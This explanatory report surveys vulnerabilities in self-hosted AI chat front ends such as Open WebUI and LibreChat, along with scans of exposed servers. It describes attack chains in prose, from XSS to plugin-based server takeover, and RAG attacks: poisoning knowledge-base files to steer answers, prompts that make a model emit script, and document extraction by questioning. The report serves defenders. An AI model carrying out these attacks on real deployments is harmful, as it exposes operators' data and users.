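Open WebUI also lets a program define a model inside a chat request without saving it. These models skipped the checks that apply when someone saves a model, so a user could list another user's file among the model's documents, and the model's search tools would return chunks of it. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3643* (August 2026), the fix in version 0.11.0 removes any document the user isn't allowed to read, before the model can use it.

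| Flaw | Container | What the attacker could do | Affected versions |
|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2026-45402 | Folder or knowledge base | Read, and with a knowledge base also overwrite | Before 0.9.5 |
| CVE-2026-54010 | Shared chat | Read and delete | Before 0.9.6 |
| CVE-2026-54012 | Saved model | Read and delete | Before 0.9.6 |
| CVE-2026-59212 | Saved model | Turn read access into overwriting and deletion | 0.9.6 until 0.10.0 |
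| CVE-2026-70487 | Model defined in a request | Read | 0.8.8 to 0.10.2 |

An operator who updated to 0.9.6 to close the holes in chats and saved models would still have had two of these five. Repairing a faulty rule by checking containers one by one is slow, and other kinds of container may still have the same flaw.

The severity scores depend on how difficult the rater thought the attack was, as with the DNS rebinding flaws. The unsaved-model flaw scores 5.3 and the search flaw that Corgea describes scores 6.5, although both let someone with an account and a file's identifier read that file.

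The model's tools need the same permission checks as the web interface. OSV's *CVE-2026-54016* describes a flaw in a built-in tool that searches for files in knowledge bases. Before version 0.9.6, a user could have the tool search any knowledge base and return details of the files there. Even a file's name, such as "redundancies-march.xlsx", can reveal sensitive information.

### Viewers and editors with too much reach

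Several flaws gave legitimate users more access than their limited roles should allow. In LibreChat, an administrator can connect a tool server, store its key and let colleagues view the connection. In versions up to 0.8.3, LibreChat decrypted the key and sent it to every viewer's browser with the other settings. According to OSV's *CVE-2026-44653* (2026), the exposed values included API keys and the secrets that LibreChat uses to identify itself to login services. A viewer could copy a key and use it outside LibreChat, where LibreChat's limits don't apply.

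Version 0.8.4 fixes this. The record also recommends that the server report only whether a key exists, and preserve the stored key when an owner edits other settings. Updating doesn't cancel a key that someone has already copied, so operators who shared such connections should also replace the keys.

LibreChat users can also let a colleague edit an agent. Suppose the office manager attaches the travel policy to a shared travel agent and to a private agent for planning budgets. In versions up to 0.8.3, a colleague who could edit the travel agent could delete the policy from the server, although unlinking it from that agent would have been enough. The budget agent would then refer to a missing file, and its owner would get no warning.

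OSV's *CVE-2026-44654* (2026) gives this flaw a score of 5.7 but is inconsistent about which version fixes it. According to its description, 0.8.4 contains the patch, but its list of affected versions includes 0.8.4 and gives 0.8.5 as the first fixed version. Updating to 0.8.5 is safe in either case.

In LibreChat 0.8.1-rc2, users with no rights to an agent could add files to the documents it searches if they knew the agent's identifier. Because the agent answers from those files, an attacker could influence its answers to everyone who used it. CVELogic lists the flaw as CVE-2025-69220, with a score of 7.1 and a fix in 0.8.2-rc2.

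Open WebUI had a comparable flaw, CVE-2026-28788. Its function for processing files in batches let users overwrite any file without checking who owned it. Anyone who could read a shared knowledge base could also get the identifiers of its files, so in practice every reader could overwrite them. As Kodem's *CVE-2026-28788* notes, the attacker then controls what the model tells other users. An attacker who overwrites the firm's travel policy removes the genuine text, whereas the hotel's brochure had to compete with it.

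The release that fixed it, 0.8.6, also corrected a flaw in how the server deleted files from knowledge bases. The server had checked that the user could edit the knowledge base named in the request, but not that the knowledge base contained the file. According to NixOS's *Open WebUI has unauthorized deletion of knowledge files*, a user could delete someone else's file by naming it in a request along with their own knowledge base.

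According to Vulners' *CVE-2026-45671 Open WebUI*, any logged-in user could permanently delete a file that appeared in a shared chat, because the server did not distinguish permission to read from permission to delete. Vulners lists versions before 0.9.0 as affected, but Positive Technologies describes the same fault in versions before 0.9.6. Either the original fix was incomplete or one of the records is wrong, so 0.9.6 is the safer minimum.

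### Two services with one secret

LibreChat retrieves documents through a separate program, the RAG API, which only LibreChat is supposed to use. The RAG API therefore checks that a request comes from LibreChat, but not which person is behind it. SBA Research's *LibreChat RAG API Authentication Bypass* (2026) explains that an ordinary user could impersonate LibreChat.

Both programs recognise callers by a JSON Web Token (JWT), a short text with a signature attached. The program that issues a token computes the signature from the text and a secret:

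```
signature = HMAC(secret, text of the token)
```

LibreChat signs a session token for each user at login, and it also uses signed tokens to identify itself to the RAG API. The signatures are made with HMAC, a standard function whose result nobody can work out without the secret. A program checks a token by repeating the calculation with the same secret and comparing the results. In the recommended set-up, LibreChat uses one secret for both kinds of token, and it offers no way to set different ones. The RAG API therefore accepts any user's session token, which lets that user read, replace or delete every document the API holds.

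The attacker also has to reach the RAG API, which is normally available only inside the operator's network. The SSRF flaw in LibreChat's Actions feature, described earlier, made this possible. Actions also let users set request headers, so an attacker could send a token with the request.

SBA Research reported the flaw in December 2025. In March 2026, LibreChat's maintainer replied that its SSRF fixes had made the flaw impossible to exploit from outside in a default installation, and closed the report. That claim holds only if the SSRF protection has no gaps. On March 27, nine days after SBA Research published its advisory, records appeared of two more ways to bypass that protection. CVELogic lists one as affecting versions up to 0.8.2 and the other as affecting all versions before 0.8.3.

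The advisory lists 0.8.1-rc2 as the tested version and doesn't list a fixed one. SBA Research recommends that LibreChat use a separate secret for the RAG API and name the intended recipient in every token, so that the RAG API can reject tokens meant for LibreChat. Until LibreChat makes these changes, operators have to keep the RAG API away from any network that users can reach. They can also give each program its own settings file, so that an intruder who gets into one program doesn't find the secrets of all the others.

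This flaw appears to have two public records, CVE-2025-41258 and CVE-2026-33265. Both were published on the same day, but CVELogic lists the first with a score of 8.0 and the second with 6.3.

### What people can learn by asking

Some operators let people question a document collection but not open the files, which protects very little. Liu and colleagues extracted text from a file called "Meeting20241015.docx" on a volunteer's AnythingLLM server, and because the server had no login, any stranger could have done the same. They give no success rate, and one demonstration can't show how reliably the method works.

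The number of questions needed to read a whole document depends on k, the number of chunks retrieved per question. If a document has 120 chunks and k is four, reading everything takes at least 30 questions. If each question retrieved four chunks at random, the expected share of the document seen after n questions would be 1 − (1 − 4/120)^n, which passes 95% at 89 questions. An employee could ask that many in an afternoon. Real searches are not random, and an attacker can cover the document faster by asking about names and headings from earlier answers. However, the model may summarise a passage or get it wrong.

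Extraction is much quicker if the attacker can query the search function directly. In Orr's test of Open WebUI, the user asked for 50 chunks at a time and received their exact text without involving a model. Setting k, the number of chunks to retrieve, to 4 on the settings page may therefore not limit every request.

In membership inference, the attacker tries to learn only whether a particular text is in the collection. The attacker needs a copy of the text, or a good guess at it, and the ability to ask questions. Suppose the firm publishes a Dify chat box for its customers. A rival who wants to know whether the collection behind it contains a certain supplier's price list can ask about a detail found only in that list and check whether the answer includes it.

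Such a test can be accurate and still mislead. Suppose it says "yes" for 90% of the texts that are in the collection and for 5% of those that are not. If half of the candidate texts are really there, a "yes" is right 95% of the time:

```
(0.5 × 0.90) / (0.5 × 0.90 + 0.5 × 0.05) = 0.95
```

If only one candidate document in a hundred is in the collection, the same "yes" is right just 15% of the time. Membership inference is therefore most useful to someone who already strongly suspects that a document is there. If the application checks permissions before it searches, chunks that the user can't read never influence the answer, so the test can't reveal anything about them.

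Embedding inversion means reconstructing a text from its embedding. The attacker must have the embedding, which an ordinary chat doesn't reveal, and usually must also be able to run the same embedding model. One method starts with a guess at the text, embeds it, compares the result with the stolen embedding and corrects the guess, repeating until the two embeddings nearly match.

Guessing can be simpler if the attacker already knows most of the text. If a chunk in the salary file reads "Anna Huber earns 61,000 euros a year", an attacker who knows the form of the sentence can embed it with every plausible figure and see which embedding matches the stolen one. With salaries in steps of 100 euros between 30,000 and 100,000, that takes 701 attempts. Guessing becomes much harder if the chunk contains other text that the attacker doesn't know.

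A thief who takes Open WebUI's whole vector database already has the chunk text, so they don't need to reconstruct it from the embeddings. Such reconstruction, called inversion, becomes a concern when an operator deletes or encrypts the text but keeps the embeddings, or sends the embeddings to an outside company, assuming they are only numbers.

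## How does a flaw in the chat page lead to control of the server?

Suppose a designer at the invented engineering firm hides a script in a chat and sends the link to the office manager, who is also the firm's Open WebUI administrator. If the page displays the chat without removing the script, the attack takes four steps:

1. The office manager opens the chat, and her browser runs the script as part of the page.
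2. The script asks the server to install a plugin written in Python. The request comes from her session, so the server treats it as hers.
3. The server accepts the request because administrators may install plugins.
4. The server runs the plugin, and the designer can now read or change anything the front end can, including the database and the provider keys.

The stored-prompt flaw CVE-2025-64495 could also lead to control of the server. The same chain exists outside chat applications. According to The Hacker News' *WordPress Comment2Shell Flaw Can Turn Anonymous Comment XSS Into RCE* (2026), an anonymous comment on a WordPress site could lead to code running on the server if a logged-in administrator opened the page.

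Only the first step, exploiting a display flaw, depends on a bug. Browsers let a page's own scripts use the viewer's session because the page couldn't work otherwise, and the plugin feature works as its developers intended. An operator can therefore stop the attack at the plugin step, even if the display flaw it exploits is not yet known.

### Plugins are meant to run code

Open WebUI has two main kinds of plugin. A Tool is Python code that the model can call, and a Function extends the application itself. Both run on the server with the same access as the front end, which covers its files, network connections, environment variables and database.

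Open WebUI's Tools and Functions can run code, read files and contact other machines. Its security policy describes this as intended behaviour, and the maintainers close any report that complains of it. Only administrators can create Functions. Creating Tools requires the `workspace.tools` permission, which is off by default for non-administrators. The policy equates granting this permission with giving someone shell access, the ability to run commands on the server.

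They have defended this position against the Zero Day Initiative, a programme that collects vulnerability reports. In January 2026 the programme published a CVE record stating that a user with few rights could run Python on the server by submitting a Tool, and it gave the supposed flaw a severity score of 8.8. Open WebUI's *CVE-2026-0766* (2026) replies that the user must already have permission to write Tools, and that notebook software such as Jupyter works the same way. The Zero Day Initiative agreed in July and withdrew the record on September 2. Open WebUI says it was a mistake to close the original report without a written explanation. Some vulnerability databases don't process withdrawals, so a scanner may still report the flaw.

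Open WebUI's argument is convincing for that record, because running the user's code is the purpose of a Tool. But the feature also makes every display flaw more serious. A stolen administrator session would expose chats and settings even without plugins, but with them it can also give the attacker control of the server. Operators who don't need plugins can switch them off with the `ENABLE_PLUGINS` setting.

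The permission is useful only if the server enforces it everywhere. Before version 0.9.5, the server checked for `workspace.tools` when a user created a Tool but not when a user changed one. According to Rapid7's *CVE-2026-45395*, a user whom the administrator had explicitly denied the permission could replace a Tool's code and have the server run it. This attack needed no script and no administrator's session. It was a vulnerability even by the maintainers' standard, because it bypassed the boundary their policy relies on.

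### Where the script enters

The stored-prompt flaw arose because the page inserted saved content as HTML. If the page had inserted it as text, the browser would have displayed any script instead of running it. But a chat page needs HTML to show headings, formulas, diagrams and embedded files, and Open WebUI's developers made mistakes in several of these features.

One mistake was in how the page displayed embedded files. According to OSV's *GHSA-9f4f-jv96-8766* (2026), the page searched each HTML tag in a message for the text that normally begins a link to a stored file. If it found that text, it inserted the whole tag unchanged, including anything else the attacker had written there. A safer page would take only the file's identifier from the message and build the tag itself.

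The script ran each time someone opened the chat. If the administrator had enabled community sharing, a user could also upload the chat to Open WebUI's public website, where the script ran in visitors' browsers. The advisory warns that such a script could have uploaded a copy of itself to each visitor's profile and spread from there, but it doesn't report that anyone did this.

The model's own answer can carry a script too. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-1722* (2026) reports that an attacker could write a prompt that led the model to produce JavaScript, which then ran in the page. The last affected version was 0.1.105, a very early release, but the attack is still instructive because it is rated as requiring no account. If an employee pasted the attacker's text into a chat, or if a search retrieved it from a document, the model could pass the script on to the page. A front end therefore has to treat the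 model's answers as untrusted input, even if the model itself is trusted.

Chat pages use further libraries to display diagrams and formulas, including Mermaid, which turns a text description into a diagram. Open WebUI used Mermaid with a permissive security setting when previewing Markdown files. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-54011* (2026) reports that a crafted diagram could run a script in the browser of the person previewing the file. A supplier could email such a file to the firm, and the script could run when someone there uploaded and previewed it.

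The formula flaw was in how Open WebUI handled errors from KaTeX, the library it uses to typeset mathematics. If a formula made KaTeX run out of working memory, the page showed the formula's source instead, but inserted it as HTML. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-70492* (2026) lists versions from 0.10.0 until 0.11.0 as affected. Tests with ordinary formulas would have missed the flaw because the faulty code ran only after an unusual failure.

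According to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-44721* (2026), anyone with permission to create models could also put a script in a shared model's details, and it would run in the browser of whoever viewed the model in the chat page.

The fix for all of these is to insert content as text wherever possible, and to pass the rest through a sanitiser such as DOMPurify immediately before display. Sanitising when the user saves the content is less reliable, because a later step such as drawing a diagram can produce new HTML. The sanitiser also has to cover previews and error messages.

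### Frames that share the application's origin

Some features need to display a complete web page, including its scripts. Sanitising the page would break it, so developers put it in a frame (a page within the page) and try to isolate the frame.

A browser gives each page an origin, which consists of the protocol, host name and port in its address. The firm's chat page might have the origin `https://chat.firm.example`. Scripts running with another origin can't read the page's contents or stored data, but any script running with this origin can use the viewer's session.

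A frame with the `sandbox` attribute loses most of its abilities, and the developer can restore some of them. The permission `allow-scripts` lets scripts run. The permission `allow-same-origin` lets the content keep the origin it would normally have. Without that second permission, the browser assigns the frame an "opaque" origin, which matches no other. If the frame's content comes from the application itself, the four combinations work like this:

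| Permissions | Do scripts run? | Origin of the frame | Can a script use the viewer's session? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Neither | No | Opaque | No |
| `allow-scripts` | Yes | Opaque | No |
| `allow-same-origin` | No | The application's | No, because none can run |
| Both | Yes | The application's | Yes |

With both permissions, a script in the frame can access the surrounding page and read the session token. It can also remove the frame's `sandbox` attribute and reload the frame without restrictions. The same permissions are much less dangerous for a video from another website, because the video's page keeps that website's origin instead of taking the application's.

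Open WebUI gave both permissions to frames embedded in chat answers. Administrators could set whether frames kept the application's origin, but the setting had no effect on these frames, according to CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-26193* (2026). An administrator who had chosen the safer option would have had no sign that it wasn't working. The attacker edited the saved chat by hand to add an embedded page, then shared the link.

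A second flaw affected citation previews, which show the document behind an answer. CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-26192* (2026) explains that an attacker could edit a saved chat and mark a cited document as HTML. When someone opened the preview to check the source, the page displayed the document's text as a web page in a frame and ran its scripts. Because the attacker had to edit a chat, there is no indication in the record that a supplier could have exploited the flaw merely by sending a document.

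An opaque origin prevents both attacks. Serving untrusted pages from a separate host name, such as `files.firm.example`, also prevents them from accessing the session, as long as the server doesn't share its session cookie with that host.

### Python that runs in the browser

When a chat contains Python code with a Run button, Open WebUI can run the code in the user's browser with Pyodide, a version of Python built for browsers. The code never reaches the server directly, so this seems safe.

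Before version 0.10.0, Pyodide ran in a background script with the application's origin. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3590* (2026), Python code could use Pyodide's link to JavaScript to send requests to the application, and the browser attached the user's session cookie to them. An attacker could share a chat containing such code and wait for a colleague to click Run. If the colleague was an administrator or could create Tools, the code could install a plugin on the server. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-59214* (2026) records the same flaw.

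The mistake that allowed this attack was giving shared code the same origin as the application. The attack didn't need a display flaw, because the page showed the code correctly and the colleague chose to run it.

Open WebUI 0.10.0 runs Pyodide in a frame with `allow-scripts` but not `allow-same-origin`. Requests from the frame to the application no longer carry the session cookie, and the browser blocks the frame from reading the replies. Python code can still fetch data from other websites that permit it. If an operator turns on `ENABLE_PYODIDE_FILE_PERSISTENCE` so that Python can keep files in the browser, Open WebUI returns to the old arrangement, with the same risk as before.

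| Flaw in Open WebUI | What carries the script or code | What the victim does | Score | Fixed in |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| PYSEC-2026-1722 | The model's answer | Views the answer | 6.1 | Later than 0.1.105 |
| GHSA-9f4f-jv96-8766 | A message with an embedded file | Opens the chat | 7.4 | 0.6.6 |
| CVE-2026-26193 | An embedded page in a saved chat | Opens the chat | 7.3 | 0.6.44 |
| CVE-2026-26192 | A cited document in a saved chat | Previews the citation | 7.3 | 0.7.0 |
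| CVE-2026-44721 | The details of a shared model | Views the model | 7.3 | 0.9.0 |
| CVE-2026-54011 | A diagram in a Markdown file | Previews the file | 8.7 | 0.9.6 |
| CVE-2026-59214 | Python code in a shared chat | Clicks Run | 7.3 | 0.10.0 |
| CVE-2026-70492 | A formula in a message | Views the message | 8.7 | 0.11.0 |

Release 0.10.0 fixed the Pyodide flaw but introduced the formula flaw. The CVSS scores are a poor guide to which flaw is worse. The formula flaw scores higher than the embedded-page flaw only because it is rated as having "changed scope". Both flaws are rated as causing no harm to availability, although an attacker who reaches the server through an administrator can switch it off. The embedded-file flaw's score of 7.4 does include that harm, but it uses the newer CVSS version 4, so it isn't directly comparable with the other scores.

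### The same picture flaw in three places

SVG is a text-based picture format, and an SVG file can contain scripts. Browsers don't run those scripts when a page shows the file as an ordinary picture, but they do when someone opens the file's own address, because the browser then treats the file as a page. If the application's server sent the file, the script runs with the application's origin.

Open WebUI let users store a profile picture as text that included a label for the picture's type. When a browser requested the picture, the server decoded the text and sent the result with that label. An attacker could label a picture as SVG, include a script in it and persuade a colleague to open the link to the picture.

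One place for such a picture was a webhook, an address through which an outside program can post messages to a group channel. vuln.today's *Open WebUI CVE-2026-45314* (2026) lists versions up to 0.9.2 as affected. The attack worked only if the administrator had enabled channels and the victim was logged in. An AI agent for security testing found the flaw, and researchers confirmed it by hand.

Pictures could also come from an outside login service, which can supply the address of a profile picture when someone signs in with another company's account. Open WebUI tried to reject SVG profile pictures, but it determined the type of these pictures from the file name's ending instead of the type the sending server declared. An SVG file could therefore pass the check, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-56398* (2026). Version 0.9.5 fixes this flaw, which scores 8.5.

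The third place was the picture of a saved model. The developers had already fixed the pictures of users and webhooks, but OSV's *CVE-2026-54013* (2026) notes that they forgot to apply the same fix to models. That flaw scores 7.6 and remained until version 0.9.6. The attacker needed permission to create models. The record says this permission is on by default, but Open WebUI's documentation says the models tab is closed to ordinary users until an administrator opens it. Operators should therefore check the setting on their installation.

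Each fix covered the code that someone had reported and left similar code elsewhere untouched. If a single function had sent every profile picture, one correction would have been enough. That function should send only pictures of a few safe types, such as PNG and JPEG, and add a `nosniff` header, which tells the browser not to guess a different type. Checking pictures when the server sends them also protects against malicious ones already in the database, which a check at upload would miss.

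### A model server that sends code

The hostile model server described earlier, which could steal a user's session token, exploited CVE-2025-64496, a flaw in Open WebUI's Direct Connections feature.

Model servers usually send an answer in small pieces, called server-sent events, so that the words appear as the model produces them. Open WebUI's page accepted events of a type named "execute" and ran their contents as JavaScript. Simonovich (2026), in *Vulnerability Discovered in Open WebUI Enables Account Takeover and Remote Code Execution*, explains that a single message to a hostile model server was enough to start the attack.

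The attack could reach the server even if the victim wasn't an administrator. In one of Simonovich's scenarios, a data analyst with the `workspace.tools` permission tries out a supposedly free alternative to GPT-4. The attacker uses the analyst's token to create a Tool, and the server runs the Tool's code. An ordinary user's token would let the attacker read that user's chats and documents but not run code on the server.

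The page was designed to run whatever an "execute" event contained, so a sanitiser wouldn't have stopped this attack. Simonovich reported the flaw on October 8, 2025. The first patch, on October 19, was incomplete. Version 0.6.35 blocks "execute" events from servers that users have added. Simonovich lists 0.6.34 as the last vulnerable version. NVD's entry for *CVE-2025-64496* lists "0.6.224", which appears to be a typo because no such release exists.

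A later flaw in Open WebUI let one user send code to another user's browser. To run Python in the browser, the server sends the code to the connection whose identifier is in the user's request. Before version 0.10.0, the server checked that the connection was active but not that it belonged to the requesting user. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3592* (2026), an attacker could share a note with an administrator, learn the identifier of the administrator's connection when the administrator opened the note, and send Python code to that connection.

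In a test on version 0.9.6, the reporter used this flaw to run commands as root, the account with full rights, inside the server's container. Much like the security policy, the advisory separates the two parts of the attack, treating an administrator's ability to install Functions as intended and the delivery of code to someone else's session as the vulnerability. The fix compares the owner of the connection with the account that sent the request.

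An older attack started from a different website. Browsers normally stop one site from reading another site's replies, but a server can allow it through cross-origin resource sharing (CORS). OSV's *GHSA-6xcp-7mpr-m7wm* describes how Open WebUI 0.3.10 allowed any website to make requests with a visitor's session. A malicious site could install a Function if an administrator clicked a link to it. The remedy is to allow cross-origin requests only from named websites, or from none.

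### Limiting what a script can do

Open WebUI keeps the session token in localStorage, a browser store that any script running under the page's origin can read. Simonovich recommends keeping the token in a short-lived HttpOnly cookie instead, which the browser sends to the server but hides from scripts. The August 2026 record of the formula flaw still describes a token in localStorage. Adding an HttpOnly cookie doesn't help while scripts can still read a copy of the token in localStorage.

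By default a token lasts four weeks, and logging out doesn't cancel it unless the operator has set up Redis, a separate data store. Changing the password cancels it, and so does the administrator's "Sign out all devices" command. Someone who suspects a token has been stolen should do one of these.

An HttpOnly cookie prevents a script from copying the token but not from using the session while the page is open. In the Pyodide attack, the Python code never had to see the cookie because the browser attached it to each request. Installing a plugin can take a single request, so an HttpOnly cookie does little to stop this last step of the attack. It is more useful against slower attacks, in which someone steals the token and reads chats for weeks.

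A content security policy, which the server sends with the page, can stop the script from running. In one common design, the server puts a new random string, called a nonce, in both the policy and its own script tags. A script that an attacker saved in a chat doesn't have the right string, so the browser doesn't run it. The policy can also stop the page from running text as code, which would have blocked the "execute" events.

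LibreChat supports such a policy but doesn't enable it by default. LibreChat's *HTTP Security Headers* advises operators to start in report-only mode, in which the browser reports violations but doesn't block them, and to enforce the policy once the reports show that it wouldn't break legitimate features. The policy is worth enforcing because the online list *LibreChat* includes two flaws from December 2025 that could lead to cross-site scripting in LibreChat.

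A policy applies only to the response that carries it. If the server sends one with the chat page but not with profile pictures, a script in an SVG file can still run when someone opens the picture's address. Even a strict policy on the chat page would therefore not have stopped attacks that used the three picture flaws.

### Commands in tool-server settings

An attacker could run commands on a LibreChat server without using a browser script or involving an administrator. The flaw, CVE-2026-22252, was in the settings for tool servers that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP). An application uses MCP to get a list of a server's tools and to send the server the model's requests to use them.

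LibreChat can contact a tool server over the network, or it can start one as a program on its own machine and exchange text with it. The second method, called stdio, needs a command that starts the program. Brown (2026), in *LibreChat MCP Stdio Remote Command Execution*, identifies three causes of the flaw:

- Any registered user could add a tool server by default.
- LibreChat accepted any command from that user.
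- It ran the command as soon as the user saved the settings, before checking that the program was a tool server.

An attacker could run a command as root inside LibreChat's container with a single request. If registration was open, a stranger could create an account and do this within minutes. The attacker could then read the keys stored in the container, contact other machines on the network or alter the files that make up the chat page. Altering those files would put a script in the browser of everyone who used LibreChat, so an attack can also move from the server to the page.

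CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-22252* (2026) lists a CVSS score of 9.1 and rates the flaw as requiring high privileges, although its description refers to any logged-in user. Changing the rating to low privileges raises the score to 9.9, which fits the flaw better.

LibreChat, like Open WebUI, is designed to let people start programs, but it had given this ability to ordinary users as well as administrators. Version 0.8.2-rc2 removes the stdio option from user settings, though administrators can still set it in the configuration file `librechat.yaml`. Checking commands against a list of allowed programs would have been weaker protection, because many common programs can start others. The online list of LibreChat's flaws includes two more from March 2026 in which tool-server connections could expose login tokens, so operators have reason to limit who may add these servers even after the update.

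### Running code somewhere else

When an application has to run users' code, the remaining protection is to isolate that code so it can do little harm. Open WebUI's *Supply Chain and Security Scanners* leaves this isolation to the operator. A container partly protects the rest of the machine, but a plugin running in the front end's container can reach everything the front end uses. Running the front end under an account with fewer rights than root limits the damage to the container but leaves the database exposed.

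Moving the code to a separate service protects more. Open WebUI gives the example of a research group that runs a re-ranking model on another machine and connects it as an outside tool server. The stated reason is that the model needs a graphics processor, but the separation also keeps the code away from the front end's files and keys. An attacker who takes over the service gets what is on that machine and whatever the front end sends to it.

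Open WebUI can similarly send Python code from chats to a Jupyter server in its own container, instead of running it in the browser with Pyodide. Before version 0.8.12, any logged-in user could run code there even after the administrator had switched code execution off, according to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2698*. The container could also contact the operator's other internal services. Operators who use Jupyter this way therefore also have to restrict the container's network access. They can test whether code execution is off by sending a harmless calculation directly to the server, rather than checking whether the Run button has disappeared.

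## How many installations are exposed, and what have attackers done to them?

Most of the flaws described so far require an account, and many also require an administrator to open something. An attacker needs neither an account nor an administrator's help when an operator puts a server on the internet with its login switched off. Published figures for the share of Open WebUI servers open to strangers range from 0.2% to 71%, largely because researchers counted different things.

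### What researchers count

Suppose the engineering firm's chat server is on the public internet. A researcher who finds it could describe it in five ways:

| Description | What the researcher observes | What it means for the firm |
|---|---|---|
| Reachable | The address returns something, perhaps only a login page | Anyone can try passwords or look for flaws |
| Responding | An API request gets a recognisable reply, which may be a refusal | The API faces the internet, but may be well protected |
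| Open registration | A stranger can create an account | The account may be useless until an administrator approves it |
| Login disabled | The application opens without an account | A stranger can use it, often as an administrator |
| Exploitable | A stranger could carry out a particular attack | The harm depends on the attack |

Proving that a server is exploitable requires carrying out the attack, which is usually illegal on someone else's machine. Researchers therefore tend to infer exploitability from the software's version number or the server's reply to a harmless request.

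Even reachable servers are hard to count. In April 2025, Hou and colleagues searched FOFA for 15 kinds of software, some of which have little to do with chat, and found 320,102 services. The total includes 37,242 records for Open WebUI and 155,423 for Ollama. These records can't be counted as separate installations, because 6,206 of them under one domain name led to only two network addresses.

Search terms can also match unrelated systems. Hou and colleagues counted 28,445 copies of Jan, a chat program, by searching for its name in page titles and for its usual port, but four months later Liu and colleagues found only eight. "Jan" is also short for January, which may explain much of the difference.

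Liu and colleagues found 126,579 Open WebUI records on FOFA in August 2025, more than three times the April count. The difference doesn't show how much installations grew, because Liu's team used a different search rule and FOFA by default returns records from nearly a whole year. Of the 9,999 records they examined, 7,758 led to a live server, and merging records with the same address left 5,896 servers. If the same proportion held for all the records, there were about 75,000 live servers. The true number was probably lower, because a longer list would contain a larger share of duplicates.

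The April survey by Hou and colleagues also found that 129,811 services, about 40% of the total, used plain HTTP, without encryption. Turning on the login doesn't protect such a server from someone who can watch its traffic, for example on the same public wireless network as an employee, because that person can read passwords and session tokens.

### Four scans of Open WebUI

Hou and colleagues randomly sampled servers running each kind of software and sent them API requests without logging in. Only 2 of 381 Open WebUI servers answered (0.52%), compared with 309 of 384 Ollama servers (80.47%). The researchers left AnythingLLM out of this test because its interfaces varied too much between installations.

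The Open WebUI figure is imprecise because it is based on only two positive results. A standard 95% confidence interval runs from about 0.06% to 1.9%, or about 25 to 700 of the 37,242 records. Hou and colleagues chose their sample sizes for a margin of error of five percentage points, which is adequate for Ollama's 80% but not for a rate this small.

In 2026, researchers at Intruder searched public records of web certificates for host names beginning with words such as "ai" or "llm". They found 24 Open WebUI servers without a login among more than 12,000, according to Marr's *From enterprise chatbots to gooner caves*.

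Cybernews, a news site with its own research team, also looked for open servers and found 98 Open WebUI servers with the login disabled and more than 2,000 with open registration, according to Compare the Cloud's *Open-Source AI Servers Hijacked with Cryptominers and Infostealers for Over a Year*. SC Media's *OpenWebUI servers targeted for extensive cryptomining* reports 12,000 servers online, while ThreatCluster's *Cybernews OpenWebUI Servers Hijacked for Crypto Mining and Data Theft*, an automatically generated summary, reports more than 15,000.

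| Scan | Date | How the researchers found servers | Open WebUI | Ollama |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hou and colleagues | April 2025 | FOFA, by page title, port and similar features | 2 of 381 sampled servers answered without a login (0.52%) | 309 of 384 sampled servers answered without a login (80.47%) |
| Liu and colleagues | August 2025 | FOFA, by software fingerprint, keeping only live servers | 4,181 of 5,896 live servers "exploitable" (70.9%); login off on 35 of 4,448 responding servers (0.8%) | 421 of 1,811 live servers "exploitable" (23.2%) |
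| Intruder, reported by Marr | 2026 | Host names in public certificate records | Login off on 24 of more than 12,000 (0.2%) | 1,652 of more than 5,200 answered a prompt (about 31%) |
| Cybernews, reported by SC Media and Compare the Cloud | March 2026 | Servers open to the internet | Login off on 98 of about 12,000 (0.8%) | Not reported |

The three direct counts of disabled logins are fairly close, ranging from 0.2% to 0.8%. Intruder's figure may be lower because Intruder searched by host name. An operator who has registered a host name and obtained a certificate has already taken some care over the installation, while a server set up in a hurry may have only a numerical address. Hou and colleagues found more than 210,000 services with no valid domain name, which a search like Intruder's would have missed.

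The Ollama figures vary more because the researchers used different tests. Hou and colleagues counted a server if any of several functions responded, though only 57% of the sample answered a request to generate text. Liu and colleagues rejected blank replies and error messages. Intruder sent the word "Hello" to servers that listed a model and counted those that replied. If the servers supplied the list of models, the 69% that didn't reply to "Hello" had still answered a stranger's request, so Intruder's figure understates how many had no login.

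### Why one figure is 71%

Liu and colleagues counted a server as exploitable if at least one API request without a login returned valid content. The content didn't have to be private, but it couldn't be just an error message or an ordinary web page. For a few addresses, they also accepted a web page, including a sign-in page.

Researchers sent 19 requests to each Open WebUI server. The 4,181 servers they classed as exploitable returned 12,343 valid replies, about three each. A volunteer's newly installed copy with login enabled also answered three of the 19, so most of these servers were probably returning only what every Open WebUI installation makes public, such as the settings for the login screen.

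The nine requests that Hou and colleagues sent to Open WebUI covered chat, embeddings, models, files and document retrieval, but not the public settings. That omission explains most of the difference between 0.52% and 70.9%. Liu and colleagues suggest that their stricter criteria, larger sample and better search rules may be responsible. Stricter criteria could explain why their Ollama rate was lower than the earlier one, but not why their Open WebUI rate was higher.

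Dify shows the same pattern. Liu and colleagues classed 82.5% of live Dify servers as exploitable. They received almost four valid replies per server, and a new installation also gave four. They found no Dify server in the sample with its login turned off.

The same rule affects the paper's headline figure, that 75% of responding servers allow API requests without authentication. Open WebUI and Dify account for about nine-tenths of the servers behind that percentage. The figure is accurate for servers that answer at least one unauthenticated request, but a reader could easily take it to mean that three-quarters of these servers give strangers access.

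Liu and colleagues also used Open WebUI's public settings to check whether login was on. It was off on 35 of the 4,448 servers that responded. If those 9,999 records were typical, the full list would have contained about 440 servers with login off.

### CVE-2025-63391

Liu and colleagues reported that Open WebUI 0.6.32 and earlier returned its configuration from `/api/config` without requiring a login. MITRE published the vulnerability record, CVE-2025-63391, in December 2025. Its severity score was 7.5.

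A visitor without an Open WebUI account gets the application's name, version and language, the available sign-in methods, and a few settings such as whether registration is open. Open WebUI's *CVE-2025-63391* (2026) states that the browser needs this information to draw the login screen. The server sends login-service secrets, storage credentials and user numbers only to people who have logged in. MITRE withdrew the CVE record on June 29, 2026, after concluding that it did not describe a security issue.

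That was the right decision, because the score assumed a complete loss of confidentiality, which doesn't occur. Operators don't need to update or change anything. The reply gives an attacker some help, since the version number shows which known flaws to try and the login field makes open servers easy to find automatically. But the attacker could also find an open server by loading its page.

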